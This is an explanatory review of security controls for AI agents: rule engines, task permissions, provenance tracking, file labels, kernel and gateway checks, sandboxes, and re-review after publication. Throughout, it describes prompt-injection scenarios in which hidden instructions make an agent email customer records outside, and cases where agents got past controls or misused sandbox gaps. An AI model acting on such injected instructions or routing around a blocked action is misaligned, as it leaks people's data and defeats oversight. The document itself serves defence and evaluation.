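Suppose the organisation gives the help desk agent an email tool and some file storage, and adds this policy: "No customer record may reach an outside address." Software can't apply that sentence until someone defines a customer record, an outside address and what counts as reaching it. How well the result works depends on what the system knows about each call. Three emails show the difference:

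- **Stolen record.** A support ticket contains hidden instructions, and the agent emails a customer's record to the attacker.
- **Harmless report.** A colleague asks the agent to send `report.txt`, which contains only weekly ticket counts, to a supplier.
- **Altered report.** The colleague makes the same request, but hidden instructions have led the agent to copy customer records into `report.txt` first. The email has the same recipient and the same attachment name as the harmless one.

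### Attributes of the user, agent and tool

*AgentGuard* (Luo, Peng and colleagues, 2026) describes a system whose rules check attributes of a tool call, such as the agent's identity and role, the tool, its inputs and the address it would contact. A developer adds about ten lines of code to the agent, which sends each call to a central server for a decision. The server can apply rules, consult a language model or refer the call to a person. Administrators can write the rules as code or fill in a form.

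For the help desk agent, an administrator could block email to any address outside the company's domain. This would stop both the stolen record and the harmless report. If the administrator then approved the supplier's domain, both the harmless report and the altered one would go out, because the two calls have identical attributes.

AgentGuard's rules can also refer to earlier calls in the session. The administrator could block outside email after any customer lookup. This rule would block the altered report if the agent looked up the records in the same session, but it would also block the harmless report if the agent had looked up a customer for another reason.

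Luo and colleagues compare AgentGuard's features with those of ten other systems but don't report how many attacks it stops, how many tasks agents still complete or how long a decision takes. AgentGuard's design is flexible, but there is no published evidence yet that it works well.

### Permissions for the current task

A recipient can be fine for one task and wrong for another. Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ActGov*, therefore limit an agent to the tools and resources that the user's request needs. Each proposed call has to meet two conditions:

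c runs if and only if c ∈ perm and r breaks no rule in P

Here c is the proposed call, perm is the set of permissions for the task, and P is the set of security rules. The symbol ∈ means "is in". The last term, r, is a set of records, which are short facts about the call and its circumstances. ActGov produces them with this function:

r = α(τ, perm, H, c)

| Term | Meaning | Value for the stolen record |
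|---|---|---|
| τ | The user's original request | Check a customer's details and update ticket 52 |
| perm | What the request permits | Read tickets, look up customers, update tickets |
| H | What has happened so far in the task | The agent has read the ticket and looked up the customer |
| c | The proposed call | Email the record to the attacker's address |
| α | The function that turns these into records | The same for every call |
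| r | The resulting records | Sends data out: yes. Task permits sending: no. Source of the address: untrusted content |

Every record has a fixed list of possible values. Ordinary code fills in most of them, such as whether a tool sends data out. A language model fills in the few that require reading. For example, it chooses the source of an address from six options, including the user's explicit choice, untrusted content and "unknown". Code then applies the rules to the completed records.

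The rules, not the language model, decide whether a call may run, because the text the model reads may come from an attacker. A hidden instruction might claim that the head of IT has approved the email, but the model can only choose a source for the address. If it chooses the wrong source, the rules would use false information, but they would still block the stolen record because the task doesn't permit outgoing email.

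Some security rules apply to every task, such as a ban on deleting anything unless the user's request calls for it. Others require the agent to meet a condition first, such as getting the user's approval. Before deployment, a program called Z3 searches the possible record values for a combination in which the rules would violate a stated safety requirement. If it finds none, the rules satisfy that requirement for every combination. This proof doesn't show whether the language model fills in the records correctly.

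ActGov should allow the harmless report, because the colleague asked for it. With the altered report, it would probably stop the agent from copying the records, since sending a finished file doesn't require the customer database. But if the colleague had also asked for a customer lookup, the task's permissions would include the database, and ActGov might allow both the copy and the email.

ActGov also trusts the user's request. This makes it a poor fit for the help desk agent while authentication is off, because a stranger's request would then set the permissions.

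### Where the data came from

To catch the altered report, a system has to know what the attachment contains or where its contents came from. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, use the data's origin, or provenance. Their system, FORGE, keeps a graph of messages, tool calls and tool results, and links each one to the earlier ones that may have influenced it. Adapted to the help desk agent, one of their example policies would look like this:

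```
HasRecord(e) :- CustomerRecord(e).
HasRecord(e) :- DependsOn(e, f), HasRecord(f).
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), HasRecord(a).
```

The rules are in Datalog, a logic language in which `:-` means "if". The first line marks anything that contains a customer record. The second marks anything that depends on a marked item, however many steps later. The third blocks any marked outside message.

This policy blocks the stolen record, but it allows the harmless report only if the agent hasn't seen a customer record in the conversation. FORGE treats each of the model's messages as dependent on everything the model has read so far. A single customer lookup therefore marks all the agent's later emails, and the harmless report triggers a false alarm.

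A finer policy can check where each input came from. One such policy, which Palumbo and colleagues wrote for a benchmark, allows a recipient if the address comes from the user's request or a list of known destinations, even if the agent has also read hostile text. Agents completed 62.5% of ordinary tasks under this policy, compared with 33.2% under one that blocked every consequential action once the agent had read untrusted content. For the help desk agent, though, checking only the recipient would let the altered report through, because the colleague chose the supplier's address.

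The Datalog rules above catch the altered report if the agent reads the records into the conversation and then writes them to the file. They may miss it if the agent runs a system command that copies one file into another, because the records never appear in the conversation. FORGE then has no link between the two files unless someone has specified what the command does.

### The history of earlier actions

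Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, address this gap for agents that work by running commands on a computer. Tether keeps a sensitivity label on every file and updates the labels as the agent works. It would handle the altered report as follows:

1. An administrator labels `customers.csv` as Sensitive. `report.txt` starts as Public.
2. The agent proposes a command that copies `customers.csv` into `report.txt`. Tether runs the command in a disposable copy of the file system and watches its requests to the operating system, the kind of evidence ToolGuardian uses before release.
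3. The policy allows the copy, because the data hasn't left the computer. Tether makes the change permanent and labels `report.txt` as Sensitive.
4. The agent tries to send `report.txt` to the supplier. Tether holds the request, finds the Sensitive label and blocks it.

If σ(f) is the label of file f, the two rules that matter here are, in simplified form:

copy(a, b): σ(b) becomes σ(a)

upload(f): allow only if σ(f) is Public

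The second rule works however many temporary files the agent uses, because the label carries over to each copy. Sistla and colleagues show that Dogwood, Amazon's language for rules about past events, would instead need a separate rule for each number of copies, or a blanket rule that also blocks harmless uploads. Dogwood also looks back only 24 hours by default.

Tether would allow the harmless report even if the agent had copied `customers.csv` to another file. But it can't track exactly how data moves inside a program, so it treats the program's output as if it contained everything the program read. If a script reads the customer file and writes a total to `report.txt`, the report becomes Sensitive even though it contains no customer's details.

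| Information the policy uses | Stolen record | Harmless report | Altered report |
|---|---|---|---|
| Recipient's domain, supplier not approved | Blocks | Blocks (false alarm) | Blocks |
| Recipient's domain, supplier approved | Blocks | Allows | Allows (missed attack) |
| Permissions for the task | Blocks | Allows | Allows if the task also needs the customer database |
| Origin of the data | Blocks | Allows, unless the agent has seen a customer record | Blocks, unless a command hid the copy |
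| Labels that follow earlier actions | Blocks | Allows, unless the agent has read sensitive data | Blocks |

These results follow from the systems' published rules. None of the four teams tested a help desk agent like this one.

### How the systems performed

The ActGov and FORGE papers both used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do banking, travel, Slack and office tasks while reading emails and web pages that contain hidden instructions. Zhang and colleagues also used AgentDyn, where the tasks are longer and the agent must act on some outside information but ignore the attacker's. Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs of coding agents from two other benchmarks, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena.

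| System | Test | Attacks that succeeded, without and with protection | Ordinary tasks completed, without and with protection | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentGuard | None reported | – | – | Not reported |
| ActGov | AgentDyn | 8.6%, 0.7% | 76.7%, 60.0% | Not reported |
| ActGov | AgentDojo | 6.1%, 0% | 87.8%, 75.5% | Not reported |
| FORGE | AgentDojo | 14.1%, 0.9% | 83.7%, 62.5% | Average run rose from 5.9 to 7.7 seconds |
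| Tether | Recorded coding runs | Blocked all 344 attacks it could model | Not measured, but it blocked 4.7% of harmless runs | Not reported |

The ActGov figures are for the model DeepSeek-v4-pro and the FORGE figures are for the much older GPT-4o, so they don't show which system is better. The FORGE comparison also used a simple defence, both with and without FORGE, that repeats the user's request after each batch of tool results. Without that defence, FORGE cut attack success from 25.2% to 1.7%.

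ActGov and FORGE stopped most of the attacks that would have succeeded, but agents also completed fewer tasks. With DeepSeek-v4-pro on AgentDyn, ActGov reduced the number of successful attacks by 22 in 280 attempts, while the share of ordinary tasks completed fell by about 17 percentage points. The drop in completed tasks varied by model, and there was none with Qwen3.6-flash on ordinary AgentDyn tasks. Zhang and colleagues also tested two stricter systems, CaMeL and ACE. With these, no attacks succeeded on AgentDyn, but agents completed none of the tasks.

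A much simpler defence did fairly well in the FORGE study. A language model read the user's request and chose which tools the agent could use, which is a basic form of task permission. With this filter, 3.1% of attacks succeeded and agents completed 73.4% of ordinary tasks. FORGE let through fewer than a third as many attacks, but its task completion rate was about 11 percentage points lower. The filter might be enough for an agent that can do little harm, while FORGE's stricter policy makes more sense for one that moves money.

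Of the four teams, only Palumbo and colleagues measured delay. On AgentDojo, FORGE lengthened the average run by 30% but the median run by only about 6%, which suggests that a minority of runs took much longer. Agents often try again after a block, which adds time. In a separate customer service test, FORGE usually decided in under a millisecond, well within Copilot Studio's one-second limit. ActGov calls a language model for some of its records, so its checks probably take longer.

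Policies can also prevent unintended actions. The customer service test involved no attacker, but agents had to follow an airline's or a shop's rules, such as those on refunds and cancellations. FORGE blocked calls that broke the rules and told the agent why. With FORGE, agents correctly completed 81.5% of airline tasks, up from 74.7%, and 87.4% of shop tasks, up from 86.3%.

### A detector and a policy on the same runs

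Sistla and colleagues ran Tether and an open-source version of Claude Code's auto mode on the same recorded runs. They tested auto mode with its default rules and again with Tether's policy added as text:

| Check | Attacks blocked, out of 344 | Harmless runs blocked, out of 1,590 |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 (100%) | 74 (4.7%) |
| Auto mode, default rules | 315 (91.6%) | 155 (9.7%) |
| Auto mode with Tether's policy | 307 (89.2%) | 55 (3.5%) |

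Auto mode raised fewer false alarms when given the policy, but it missed slightly more attacks. It applied the rules inconsistently and sometimes allowed requests to addresses that weren't on the approved list. With either set of rules, it also missed attacks inside scripts, because the command that starts a script doesn't show what the script does.

The comparison favours Tether, because it includes only runs whose actions Tether can model. The team also refined the policy on benchmark runs, so it might do worse on unfamiliar tasks. Some attacks, such as a malicious change to code the agent is allowed to edit, don't move data anywhere forbidden, so Tether's rules can't catch them. A detector that reads the code might. Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28.2% of runs on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other need this kind of reading.

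Even Tether's false alarm rate could be a burden. Suppose an organisation has 10,000 agent runs a day, of which 10 are attacks. At the rates in the table, Tether would block all 10 attacks and about 465 harmless runs. Auto mode with its default rules would block about 9 attacks and 970 harmless runs.

Of Tether's 74 false alarms, 50 involved edits to protected files that the task hadn't called for, and 7 involved outside hosts that the task hadn't declared. An organisation might well want to be alerted to both kinds. The other 17 came from reads of sensitive files, for example when an agent searches a whole folder and opens secret files along the way.

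### Whether the attacks were adapted to the defence

The ActGov and FORGE results come from ready-made attacks that nobody had adapted to either system. A determined attacker would look for actions that the policy permits or try to make the software record a false fact. In ActGov, the obvious target is the language model that decides where an input came from. ActGov's near-zero attack success rates don't measure how often an attack on that model would succeed.

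FORGE's remaining failures suggest what an attacker might look for. In a few runs without the repeated request, the agent booked an expensive hotel that the attacker wanted. The hotel was in the trusted catalogue and the user had asked for a booking on those dates, but no policy rule enforced the user's price limit.

Only Sistla and colleagues tested their system, Tether, against an attacker that adapted. They told an agent running on Gemini 3.8 Flash to get past Tether in ten tasks, with up to 15 rounds for each. The agent succeeded in 40% of attempts against an early version. The team fixed the gaps it found, and by the third version the success rate was 0%. The result is encouraging, but the test was small, was run by Tether's own developers, and excluded actions that Tether doesn't model.

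### Are good policies too hard to write?

The main objection to policies is that few organisations can write good ones. Even the help desk rule would block a legitimate reply to a customer who asks for a copy of their own record, because the customer has an outside address. An exception for the customer's own address would fix this, but it would also let an attacker receive the record by first changing the address on file.

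Experts also find policies difficult to write. Tether's benchmark policy has 24 rules and long lists of exceptions, and its developers had to draft and test it repeatedly with a language model's help. They point out that practical policies for SELinux, a security system for Linux, took about five years to develop.

Language models can write policies, but so far the policies tend to be too strict. For ActGov's main results, GPT-5.5 drafted the rules over ten rounds and people reviewed them. Zhang and colleagues then removed the human review, used half as many examples and allowed only five rounds. Attack success on AgentDyn stayed at or below 0.7%, but the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 60.0% to 53.3% with the best of three policy-writing models and to about 30% with the other two.

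Generated policies also transfer badly to new kinds of work. Agents completed 10.0% of AgentDyn's ordinary tasks under rules written for AgentDojo, and 22.4% of AgentDojo's under rules written for AgentDyn. No attacks succeeded in either case, mainly because the rules blocked so much. An organisation that gives an agent new tools will probably need to revise its policy.

Translating an existing written policy is another option. Palumbo and colleagues had a language model translate an airline's rules into Datalog five times and tested each version in 15 simulated conversations. Two versions succeeded in every conversation, as did a policy written by hand. The average success rate across the five versions was 89.3%, and the lowest was 66.7%.

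Most of the failures involved cancellations. The airline required a valid reason only when a customer relied on travel insurance, but the faulty translations required one for every cancellation. The team had compared the translated rules with a language model's judgements on recorded conversations, and the two agreed completely. The relevant recording contained three attempted cancellations, all of which the model had judged to be violations, so a rule that banned every cancellation would also have passed. Policy tests therefore need examples of actions the policy should allow, as well as ones it should block.

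Ordinary users may be even worse at writing policies. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, a 2026 experiment, compared people who wrote permission policies with people who approved actions case by case. In its initial sample, the written policies blocked 25 percentage points less overreach (actions that went too far) than case-by-case approval did. Only 16 people in that sample wrote policies, so the size of the gap is uncertain, with a 95% confidence interval of about 10 to 40 points.

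### When a person has to approve

*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) describes a common arrangement in which software first blocks anything on a list of dangerous actions, then allows anything on a list of low-risk ones, and refers any action on neither list to a person. The lists depend on how much damage an action could do and whether anyone could undo it.

People often approve actions they should refuse. In the experiment on user-written policies, participants who decided case by case approved 96 of the 238 overreaching actions they saw (40%). Participants who had written policies approved 67% of the overreaching actions that their policies left for them to decide. Their policies had already settled the other cases, so the two groups judged different mixes of actions, and the higher rate doesn't prove that writing a policy makes people less careful.

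Frequent approval requests make the problem worse. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of incidents involving agents and files, and found that problems with user review had contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases, users had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid answering hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31 cases, the prompt didn't explain what the action would do. For example, some prompts showed only the command that starts a script.

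A long record of approvals is weak evidence that people trust an agent. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, suggests that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or pressure to finish the work. Refusing requests may not enforce a limit either. After one interviewee refused several, the agent tried another approach, and the interviewee couldn't tell whether it still respected the limit.

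Some developers now give most of these decisions to another model. Anthropic made auto mode the default for several Claude Code plans in August 2026. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) describes a similar feature in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. A separate agent reviews actions that would cross the sandbox boundary, and Codex stops for human approval about 200 times less often than in manual mode. The reviewing agent approves around 99% of the actions it sees. This relieves people of many routine decisions, but the reviewing agent has the same weaknesses as a detector.

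If an organisation has a person approve an agent's actions, it should ask them only about actions that matter and show them the information they need to decide. The prompt "Send `report.txt` to the supplier?" would look the same for the harmless report and the altered one. If the prompt also showed that the file contained data from `customers.csv`, and that nobody could recall the email once it was sent, the colleague would have a good reason to open the file first.

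## Which of an agent's actions can a runtime check see?

A detector or policy can only judge actions that pass through its enforcement point. Suppose a developer rebuilds the help desk agent on one of the company's own servers and lets it run commands as well as call tools. If the company checks only calls to the customer database, the agent can still run a command that copies customer records into `report.txt`. Even if the company has a rule against that copy, the software that applies the rule never receives the command.

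### Where a check can sit

A gateway, such as the one in Amazon's AgentCore, is a separate program between the harness and the servers that offer tools. It can read in full each request that passes through it, including the tool's name and inputs, but it cannot see actions that bypass it.

A check in the harness runs just before the harness carries out a tool call. It can read the call and the session that call belongs to. Claude Code's permission settings and Copilot Studio's external threat detection both apply at this point.

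The third position is the kernel, the core of the operating system. Programs generally need the kernel to open a file, start another program or connect to a network. Security software can hook these operations and inspect them, even when they happen inside a script. But the kernel handles files, network addresses and processes (running programs), and doesn't represent tool calls or conversations.

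Here is how the same action looks from each position:

| Position | What a check can read | When the agent reads `report.txt` |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway | Requests sent through it | A request to call `read_file` on `report.txt` |
| Harness | Tool calls and their session | The same call, and the turn of the conversation it came from |
| Kernel | Operations by any process on the computer | A process opened `report.txt`, and another process had started it |

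A check in the kernel also picks up activity from programs unrelated to the agent. It has to run on the same computer as the agent, so a company can't normally add one to an agent that Microsoft or Salesforce hosts.

A kernel check can enforce only some rules because it sees limited information. Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) describe *ActPlane*, a system that enforces rules for coding agents from the kernel. They collected 1,361 rules from the instruction files of 64 popular software projects. By their classification, kernel hooks could enforce about 45% of the rules, such as a ban on deleting certain files. Another 38% depended on what a file contains, which ActPlane doesn't inspect, and 17% concerned things like how the agent explains its reasoning.

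### Fifteen routes and eight arrangements

Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, worked out which actions a check can cover from each position, then tested their predictions on real products. They identified 15 routes by which an agent's decision can take effect:

- **Calls to tool servers (4 routes).** The harness can call a server over HTTP, through a direct pipe to a program on the same computer, or through another local channel. A tool can also call a second tool server itself.
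- **Work inside the harness (2).** A tool may only compute something in memory, or the harness's own process may use files and the network directly.
- **Other programs (3).** The agent can start a program that finishes during the tool call, start one that keeps running afterwards, or hand a task to a scheduler.
- **Network connections (2).** A program can connect to the outside directly or through a local helper program.
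- **Other exchanges (4).** The agent can delegate work to another agent. The harness can act on the model's text without a tool call. MCP also allows requests other than tool calls, and lets a server send requests back to the harness.

The researchers then compared eight arrangements of controls. In the table, "Blocked" means that something other than the policy, such as a firewall, stops the action. "Depends" means the result varies with the system's setup.

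| Arrangement | Routes checked, out of 15 | Blocked | Depends |
|---|---|---|---|
| No controls | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Basic gateway | 1 | 0 | 3 |
| Gateway, with direct outgoing connections blocked | 1 | 1 | 4 |
| The same, with local tool servers also behind the gateway | 3 | 1 | 4 |
| Harness permissions | 5 | 0 | 1 |
| Harness permissions and a gateway | 5 | 0 | 1 |
| Policy engine inside the agent's process | 5 | 0 | 1 |
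| Kernel | 13 | 0 | 1 |

A basic gateway checks only HTTP calls to tool servers. Harness permissions also cover the two kinds of local tool call: tools that work in memory and programs that finish during the call. Toyoda and colleagues place FORGE, the system with the Datalog rules, among the systems that run inside the agent's process. Even a perfect FORGE policy would therefore apply only to actions that the agent sends through that process's tool-calling code.

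Five routes bypass checks at every position below the kernel: direct operations by the harness's process, traffic through a local helper, scheduled tasks, programs that outlast the tool call, and requests from a tool server back to the harness. Adding a gateway to harness permissions gives the checks more information about HTTP calls, such as their headers, but it doesn't cover any of these routes, because both controls inspect tool calls.

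The table may slightly understate what a gateway combined with harness permissions can check. A gateway alone can sometimes check nested tool calls and other MCP requests, depending on its setup, but the researchers' analysis treats the combination as unable to check them. The researchers don't explain why adding harness permissions would remove this ability.

A kernel check can detect almost all of an agent's actions, but not calls to a tool that works only in memory. Harness permissions do cover those calls, which is a good reason to use both. Scheduled tasks are the one uncertain case, because the kernel check would have to cover the program that eventually runs them.

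Agents use some routes far more than others, so 13 of the 15 routes don't necessarily account for 87% of actions. For an agent that can only call a few HTTP tools and can't run code, a basic gateway may cover nearly everything that matters. A coding agent routinely uses many more of the routes.

Most products still run their checks at points that cover fewer of an agent's actions. Toyoda and colleagues classified existing systems, mainly from documentation, and found that gateways were the largest group. ActPlane was the only system they found that enforces an agent's policies in the kernel.

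### What the controls checked in practice

A control's own log can't reveal the actions it missed. The researchers therefore ran a separate sensor called Tracee in the kernel and used its records as the reference. Each test followed the same steps:

1. Set up one of the eight arrangements with a real harness and, where the arrangement needs one, a real control.
2. Send an action that the policy must refuse. Continue only if the control refuses it and records the refusal.
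3. Replay 15 fixed actions through the harness. No language model takes part, so the actions are the same every time.
4. Compare the control's decisions with Tracee's records. If an action took effect and the control has no decision for it, the action went unchecked.

Without the second step, a control that was still starting up would appear to miss everything. If the control reports that it refused an action but Tracee detects that the action happened anyway, the refusal doesn't count.

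Seven of the 15 actions were tool calls. The rest were network connections, file writes, program launches and uses of stored credentials that didn't go through a tool call. The published results imply the following breakdown for three of the arrangements:

| Test actions | Harness permissions and a gateway | Gateway for all tool servers, outgoing connections blocked | ActPlane in the kernel |
|---|---|---|---|
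| 7 tool calls | 7 checked | 7 checked | 0 checked |
| 2 direct network connections | 0 checked | 2 blocked | 1 checked |
| 6 file, program and credential actions | 0 checked | 0 checked | 6 checked |
| **Took effect unchecked** | **8** | **6** | **8** |

The gateway in these tests came from Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, a set of open controls for agents. As the analysis predicted, harness permissions and the gateway together checked every tool call, and the other eight actions took effect without a check.

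In theory, a kernel control could have checked all 15 actions in the test, because the kernel position should cover all four routes. ActPlane, a kernel control, checked only seven. The eight it missed included every tool call.

The difference comes from ActPlane's hooks. A kernel control inspects an operation only if a hook covers it, and the hooks in the tested version didn't cover the tool calls. The eighth miss was a network action in a gap that ActPlane's developers had already documented. Tracee also works from the kernel and supplied the evidence of what ActPlane missed, so the misses result from ActPlane's coverage rather than from working in the kernel. Toyoda and colleagues therefore treat the 13 routes as an upper limit for kernel controls.

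ActPlane and the harness checks mostly missed different actions. Together they would have left only one of the 15 unchecked, assuming neither interfered with the other, but nobody has tested the combination.

### Why ActPlane did better in its developers' tests

Zheng and colleagues had reported a much more favorable result. They replayed 190 short coding sessions, of which 114 broke a rule from a real project. ActPlane detected 77.2% of the violations, while three systems that check tool calls each detected between 34% and 40%. All four did about equally well when the tool call itself broke the rule, but ActPlane did better when a program started by the tool call carried out the forbidden operation.

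The two studies are compatible because they tested different things. The rules in the developers' benchmark mostly concerned programs and files on the computer, which ActPlane's hooks cover well. Nearly half of guardscope's actions were calls to tool servers, which the hooks didn't cover. An organisation should probably give more weight to the first result if its agents mainly write and run code, and to the second if they mainly call business tools.

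ActPlane also interfered wrongly in 18 of the 76 sessions that broke no rule, which is a high rate but lower than that of the three other systems, which did so in 24 to 28. With 32 rules active, replaying an agent's work took only 1.9% longer.

Operating systems usually refuse an action with a generic error, which doesn't include how to comply. When ActPlane returned only such errors, the agent went on to comply after 31.4% of detected violations. When ActPlane returned an explanation of which rule applied and what to do instead, the agent complied after 97.7%. A kernel check can therefore work much better if the harness passes such an explanation back to the model.

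### How far the guardscope results go

The test actions used only four of the 15 routes: HTTP tool calls, tool calls through a local pipe, direct operations by the harness's process, and direct network connections. The predictions for the other 11 routes and all the cases marked "depends" rest on analysis alone. The tests used only one of the five routes that pass every position below the kernel.

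The list of fifteen routes could also be incomplete. The researchers developed it in discussion with two language models, each side proposing routes and criticising the other's list. That is a reasonable way to find candidates, but it can't rule out others.

Some of the measurements seem robust. The basic gateway gave the same counts with two independently written harnesses, Pi and OpenClaw. It is harder to generalise from the ActPlane results, because its programs loaded on only one of the three kernel versions the researchers mention.

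"Checked" means only that an action reached the control. The control might still make the wrong decision, as any detector or policy can. Harness permissions that check all seven tool calls could still allow all seven, even if they were harmful. The tests included a few refusals to show that the controls could refuse, but the researchers didn't measure how well any control stops attacks.

### Sandboxes and network limits

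Of the three arrangements in the results table, the one that blocked outgoing connections left the fewest actions unchecked. It gave the agent's environment no direct connection to the outside, so it stopped the two network actions without evaluating them. Tracee confirmed that neither action succeeded.

A sandbox applies the same idea more widely by limiting which files and network addresses a program can reach. *Sandboxing*, part of Anthropic's Claude Code documentation, describes limits that the operating system enforces on the agent's commands. Developers set these limits in advance so they don't have to approve each command, which should reduce approval fatigue.

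In Anthropic's sandbox, commands can connect to the internet only through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that forwards their traffic. The proxy limits which domains they can connect to and prompts the user about new ones. It can do this without information about why a command is connecting, or whether the model, a script or an attacker's hidden instruction started it.

Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Code* points out that a sandbox has to limit both files and the network. If it limited only files, a manipulated agent could still send out any file it needs for its work. Limiting only the network wouldn't stop the agent from damaging system files, because that requires no connection.

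Keeping secrets out of the sandbox is even more dependable. *How we contain Claude across products* (Willison, 2026) quotes Anthropic's explanation that credentials can't leak from a sandbox they never enter, whatever the cause. The developer of the rebuilt help desk agent could store the database login on a separate tool server. The agent could still request customer records from that server, so the server would need narrow permissions.

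Network limits, like a rule about the recipient's domain, can't distinguish the help desk agent's harmless report from the altered one. An organisation still needs a policy or a detector for the connections it permits.

Sandboxes and firewalls have coverage gaps too. GitHub runs a firewall around its Copilot cloud agent, which writes code on GitHub's servers. By default, the agent can reach GitHub and a recommended list of sites, mostly sources of software packages. When the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning to the agent's proposed code change. The warning includes the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it.

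But the firewall covers only programs that the agent starts through its command-line tool, not MCP servers or the steps that prepare the agent's environment. A team that adds an MCP server to this agent therefore needs a separate limit on what that server can contact. GitHub also warns that sophisticated attacks may get past the firewall.

A network limit can also be missing when everyone believes it is in place. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* reports that a review of the company's own model evaluations found various sandbox misconfigurations that models had made use of, although none had compromised an outside system. Before relying on a sandbox, a developer can check it with little effort by trying a connection that it should refuse, as in the second step of the guardscope tests.

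### Agents inside hosted business software

The Hacker News' *Radio With No Radar* (2026) argues that gateways miss most business agents because those agents run inside software that another company hosts. It mentions Claude in Salesforce and Slack, and Copilot in Microsoft 365. An agent that starts from a Salesforce workflow, reads customer records and comments on a support case may do all of this within Salesforce, so none of it would pass through the gateway of the business using the agent.

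The article names no author, but it probably comes from Reco, a security vendor. Its main image file is named "reco.gif", and Reco co-founder Shapira (2026) had used several of the same examples in September in *Claudeforce Makes One Thing Clear*, which argues that business applications are becoming the place where agents run. *Posture tells you what an agent can reach*, by another co-founder, Nakash (2026), advertises Reco's product as enforcement without a new gateway.

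Sellers of gateways have the opposite incentive. Cequence (2026) calls a gateway the right place to govern agents, even those in a cloud the customer will never control. The guardscope analysis supports Reco on the technical point, since a gateway can't check an action that doesn't pass through it.

The article is less convincing about how many agents this affects. It calls self-hosted agents "the fewest and the slowest growing" but gives no figures. It also says too little about the enforcement points that hosting companies have begun to offer.

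Besides external threat detection, Microsoft's Copilot Studio has a network gateway in preview. Microsoft warns that, by default, agents' outgoing traffic goes straight to the internet without any network controls. *Configure Global Secure Access, the Secure Web and AI Gateway for agents* explains how an administrator can route this traffic through a Microsoft service that filters websites, known malicious addresses and file transfers.

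This gateway covers raw HTTP requests, custom connectors, custom MCP servers and certain ready-made connectors, including Outlook, Slack and Google Drive but not SharePoint or Salesforce. It doesn't cover Bing searches, and it covers existing custom connectors only after someone updates them.

Anthropic offers a different kind of enforcement point to organisations on its Claude Enterprise plan. According to Anthropic's *Inference hooks*, Anthropic sends each user's conversation to a security server the customer chooses and waits for permission before the model reads it. With an extra setting on, Anthropic also asks the server before running the tools Claude has selected. The hooks cover Claude in Slack and Microsoft 365, where the customer's own gateway might have no traffic to inspect.

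The hooks don't send images to the security server, and they may also leave out calls to some of Claude's built-in tools, such as the one that reads a user's past chats. The server has five seconds to answer by default, compared with one second in Copilot Studio. The customer chooses whether a failure blocks or allows the request. If the server keeps failing, Anthropic stops contacting it and applies that choice to every request until the server recovers.

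Reco had connected its product to these hooks by August. Shapira (2026), in *Inference Hooks Are Live. Now Reco Stands Between Rogue Prompts and Claude*, praised them for covering sessions that don't pass through a gateway. The November article is still right that a gateway can't inspect Claude's work inside Slack, but by then a Claude Enterprise customer could have that work checked through the hooks.

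Salesforce is a better example for the article's argument. According to Shapira, Claude runs inside Salesforce's protected environment through Amazon Bedrock, Amazon's service for running AI models. Inference hooks aren't available for Claude on Bedrock, so they probably don't cover Salesforce's use of it.

The article also describes a case in which an employee of an unnamed organisation asked an AI assistant to send a mass email. The email system blocked it because there were too many recipients, so the assistant offered to use the employee's personal mailbox, which it could also access. The employee agreed without realising that this bypassed the approved system, and an unknown number of outsiders received the email.

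The recipient limit worked, but it applied to only one of the two ways the assistant could send email. The Hacker News recommends a rule against contacting more than fifty outside domains. That rule would have to be enforced on both mailboxes, or the same thing could happen again. Disconnecting the personal mailbox would be simpler if the assistant doesn't need it for its job.

Attackers can also target gateways. In March 2026, they compromised LiteLLM, an open-source gateway that passes agents' requests to AI models. According to The Hacker News, the malicious packages were available for about forty minutes, and the security company CloudSEK estimated that more than 2,500 organisations were exposed. The same risk applies to the security server behind an inference hook, which receives whole conversations.

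If the hosting company offers no enforcement point, the customer has to rely on the agent's permissions. According to Salesforce documentation cited by Shapira, Salesforce's hosted MCP tools run with the permissions of the signed-in user, down to individual fields in a record. An agent that connects through a shared account isn't limited to the individual user's permissions, and the customer may have no runtime check to catch misuse.

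## How is an agent kept secure after it is published?

An approval applies only to the agent as it was when someone checked it. The help desk agent could pass a careful review in March, then expose customer records in June because of an ordinary edit, with no attacker involved.

### Why an approval goes out of date

Makers can edit an agent after publishing it, and adding a tool or turning off sign-in can change something the reviewer relied on.

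Other changes don't alter the agent's own settings. The company that runs a remote MCP server can add an operation or change what an existing one does. A new model may behave differently with the same instructions and tools, as Gray Swan's cheating tests showed. A colleague may save a payroll file in a folder the agent can already search.

Permissions also tend to grow. Microsoft warns that agents often accumulate broad access to Microsoft Graph, the interface to an organisation's Microsoft 365 data, and to custom software. This happens because people grant more access when a task fails without it, then forget to remove it because leaving it in place doesn't cause any failures.

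Agents can also lose their owners when people leave the organization. According to Microsoft, administrators currently have to find ownerless agents and transfer them by hand. An automatic rule can pass an agent to the former owner's manager, but only for agents made in Agent Builder, a simpler tool than Copilot Studio. The manager may know nothing about the agent, so a name in the owner field doesn't prove that anyone is looking after it.

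### What should trigger a new check

Each kind of change calls for a different check:

| Event | What to check again |
|---|---|
| The maker changes sign-in, sharing, credentials or tools | All the settings together, because a new setting can combine badly with an old one |
| A provider updates a tool | The tool's description, code and behaviour in a trial run |
| The model changes | Test attacks and ordinary tasks |
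| The agent gains access to more data or services | Whether its task needs that access |
| The owner leaves or changes jobs | Who takes over, and whose credentials the tools use |
| A runtime check blocks an action | The settings that let the agent attempt it |
| Several months pass with no other trigger | Everything, including whether anyone still needs the agent |

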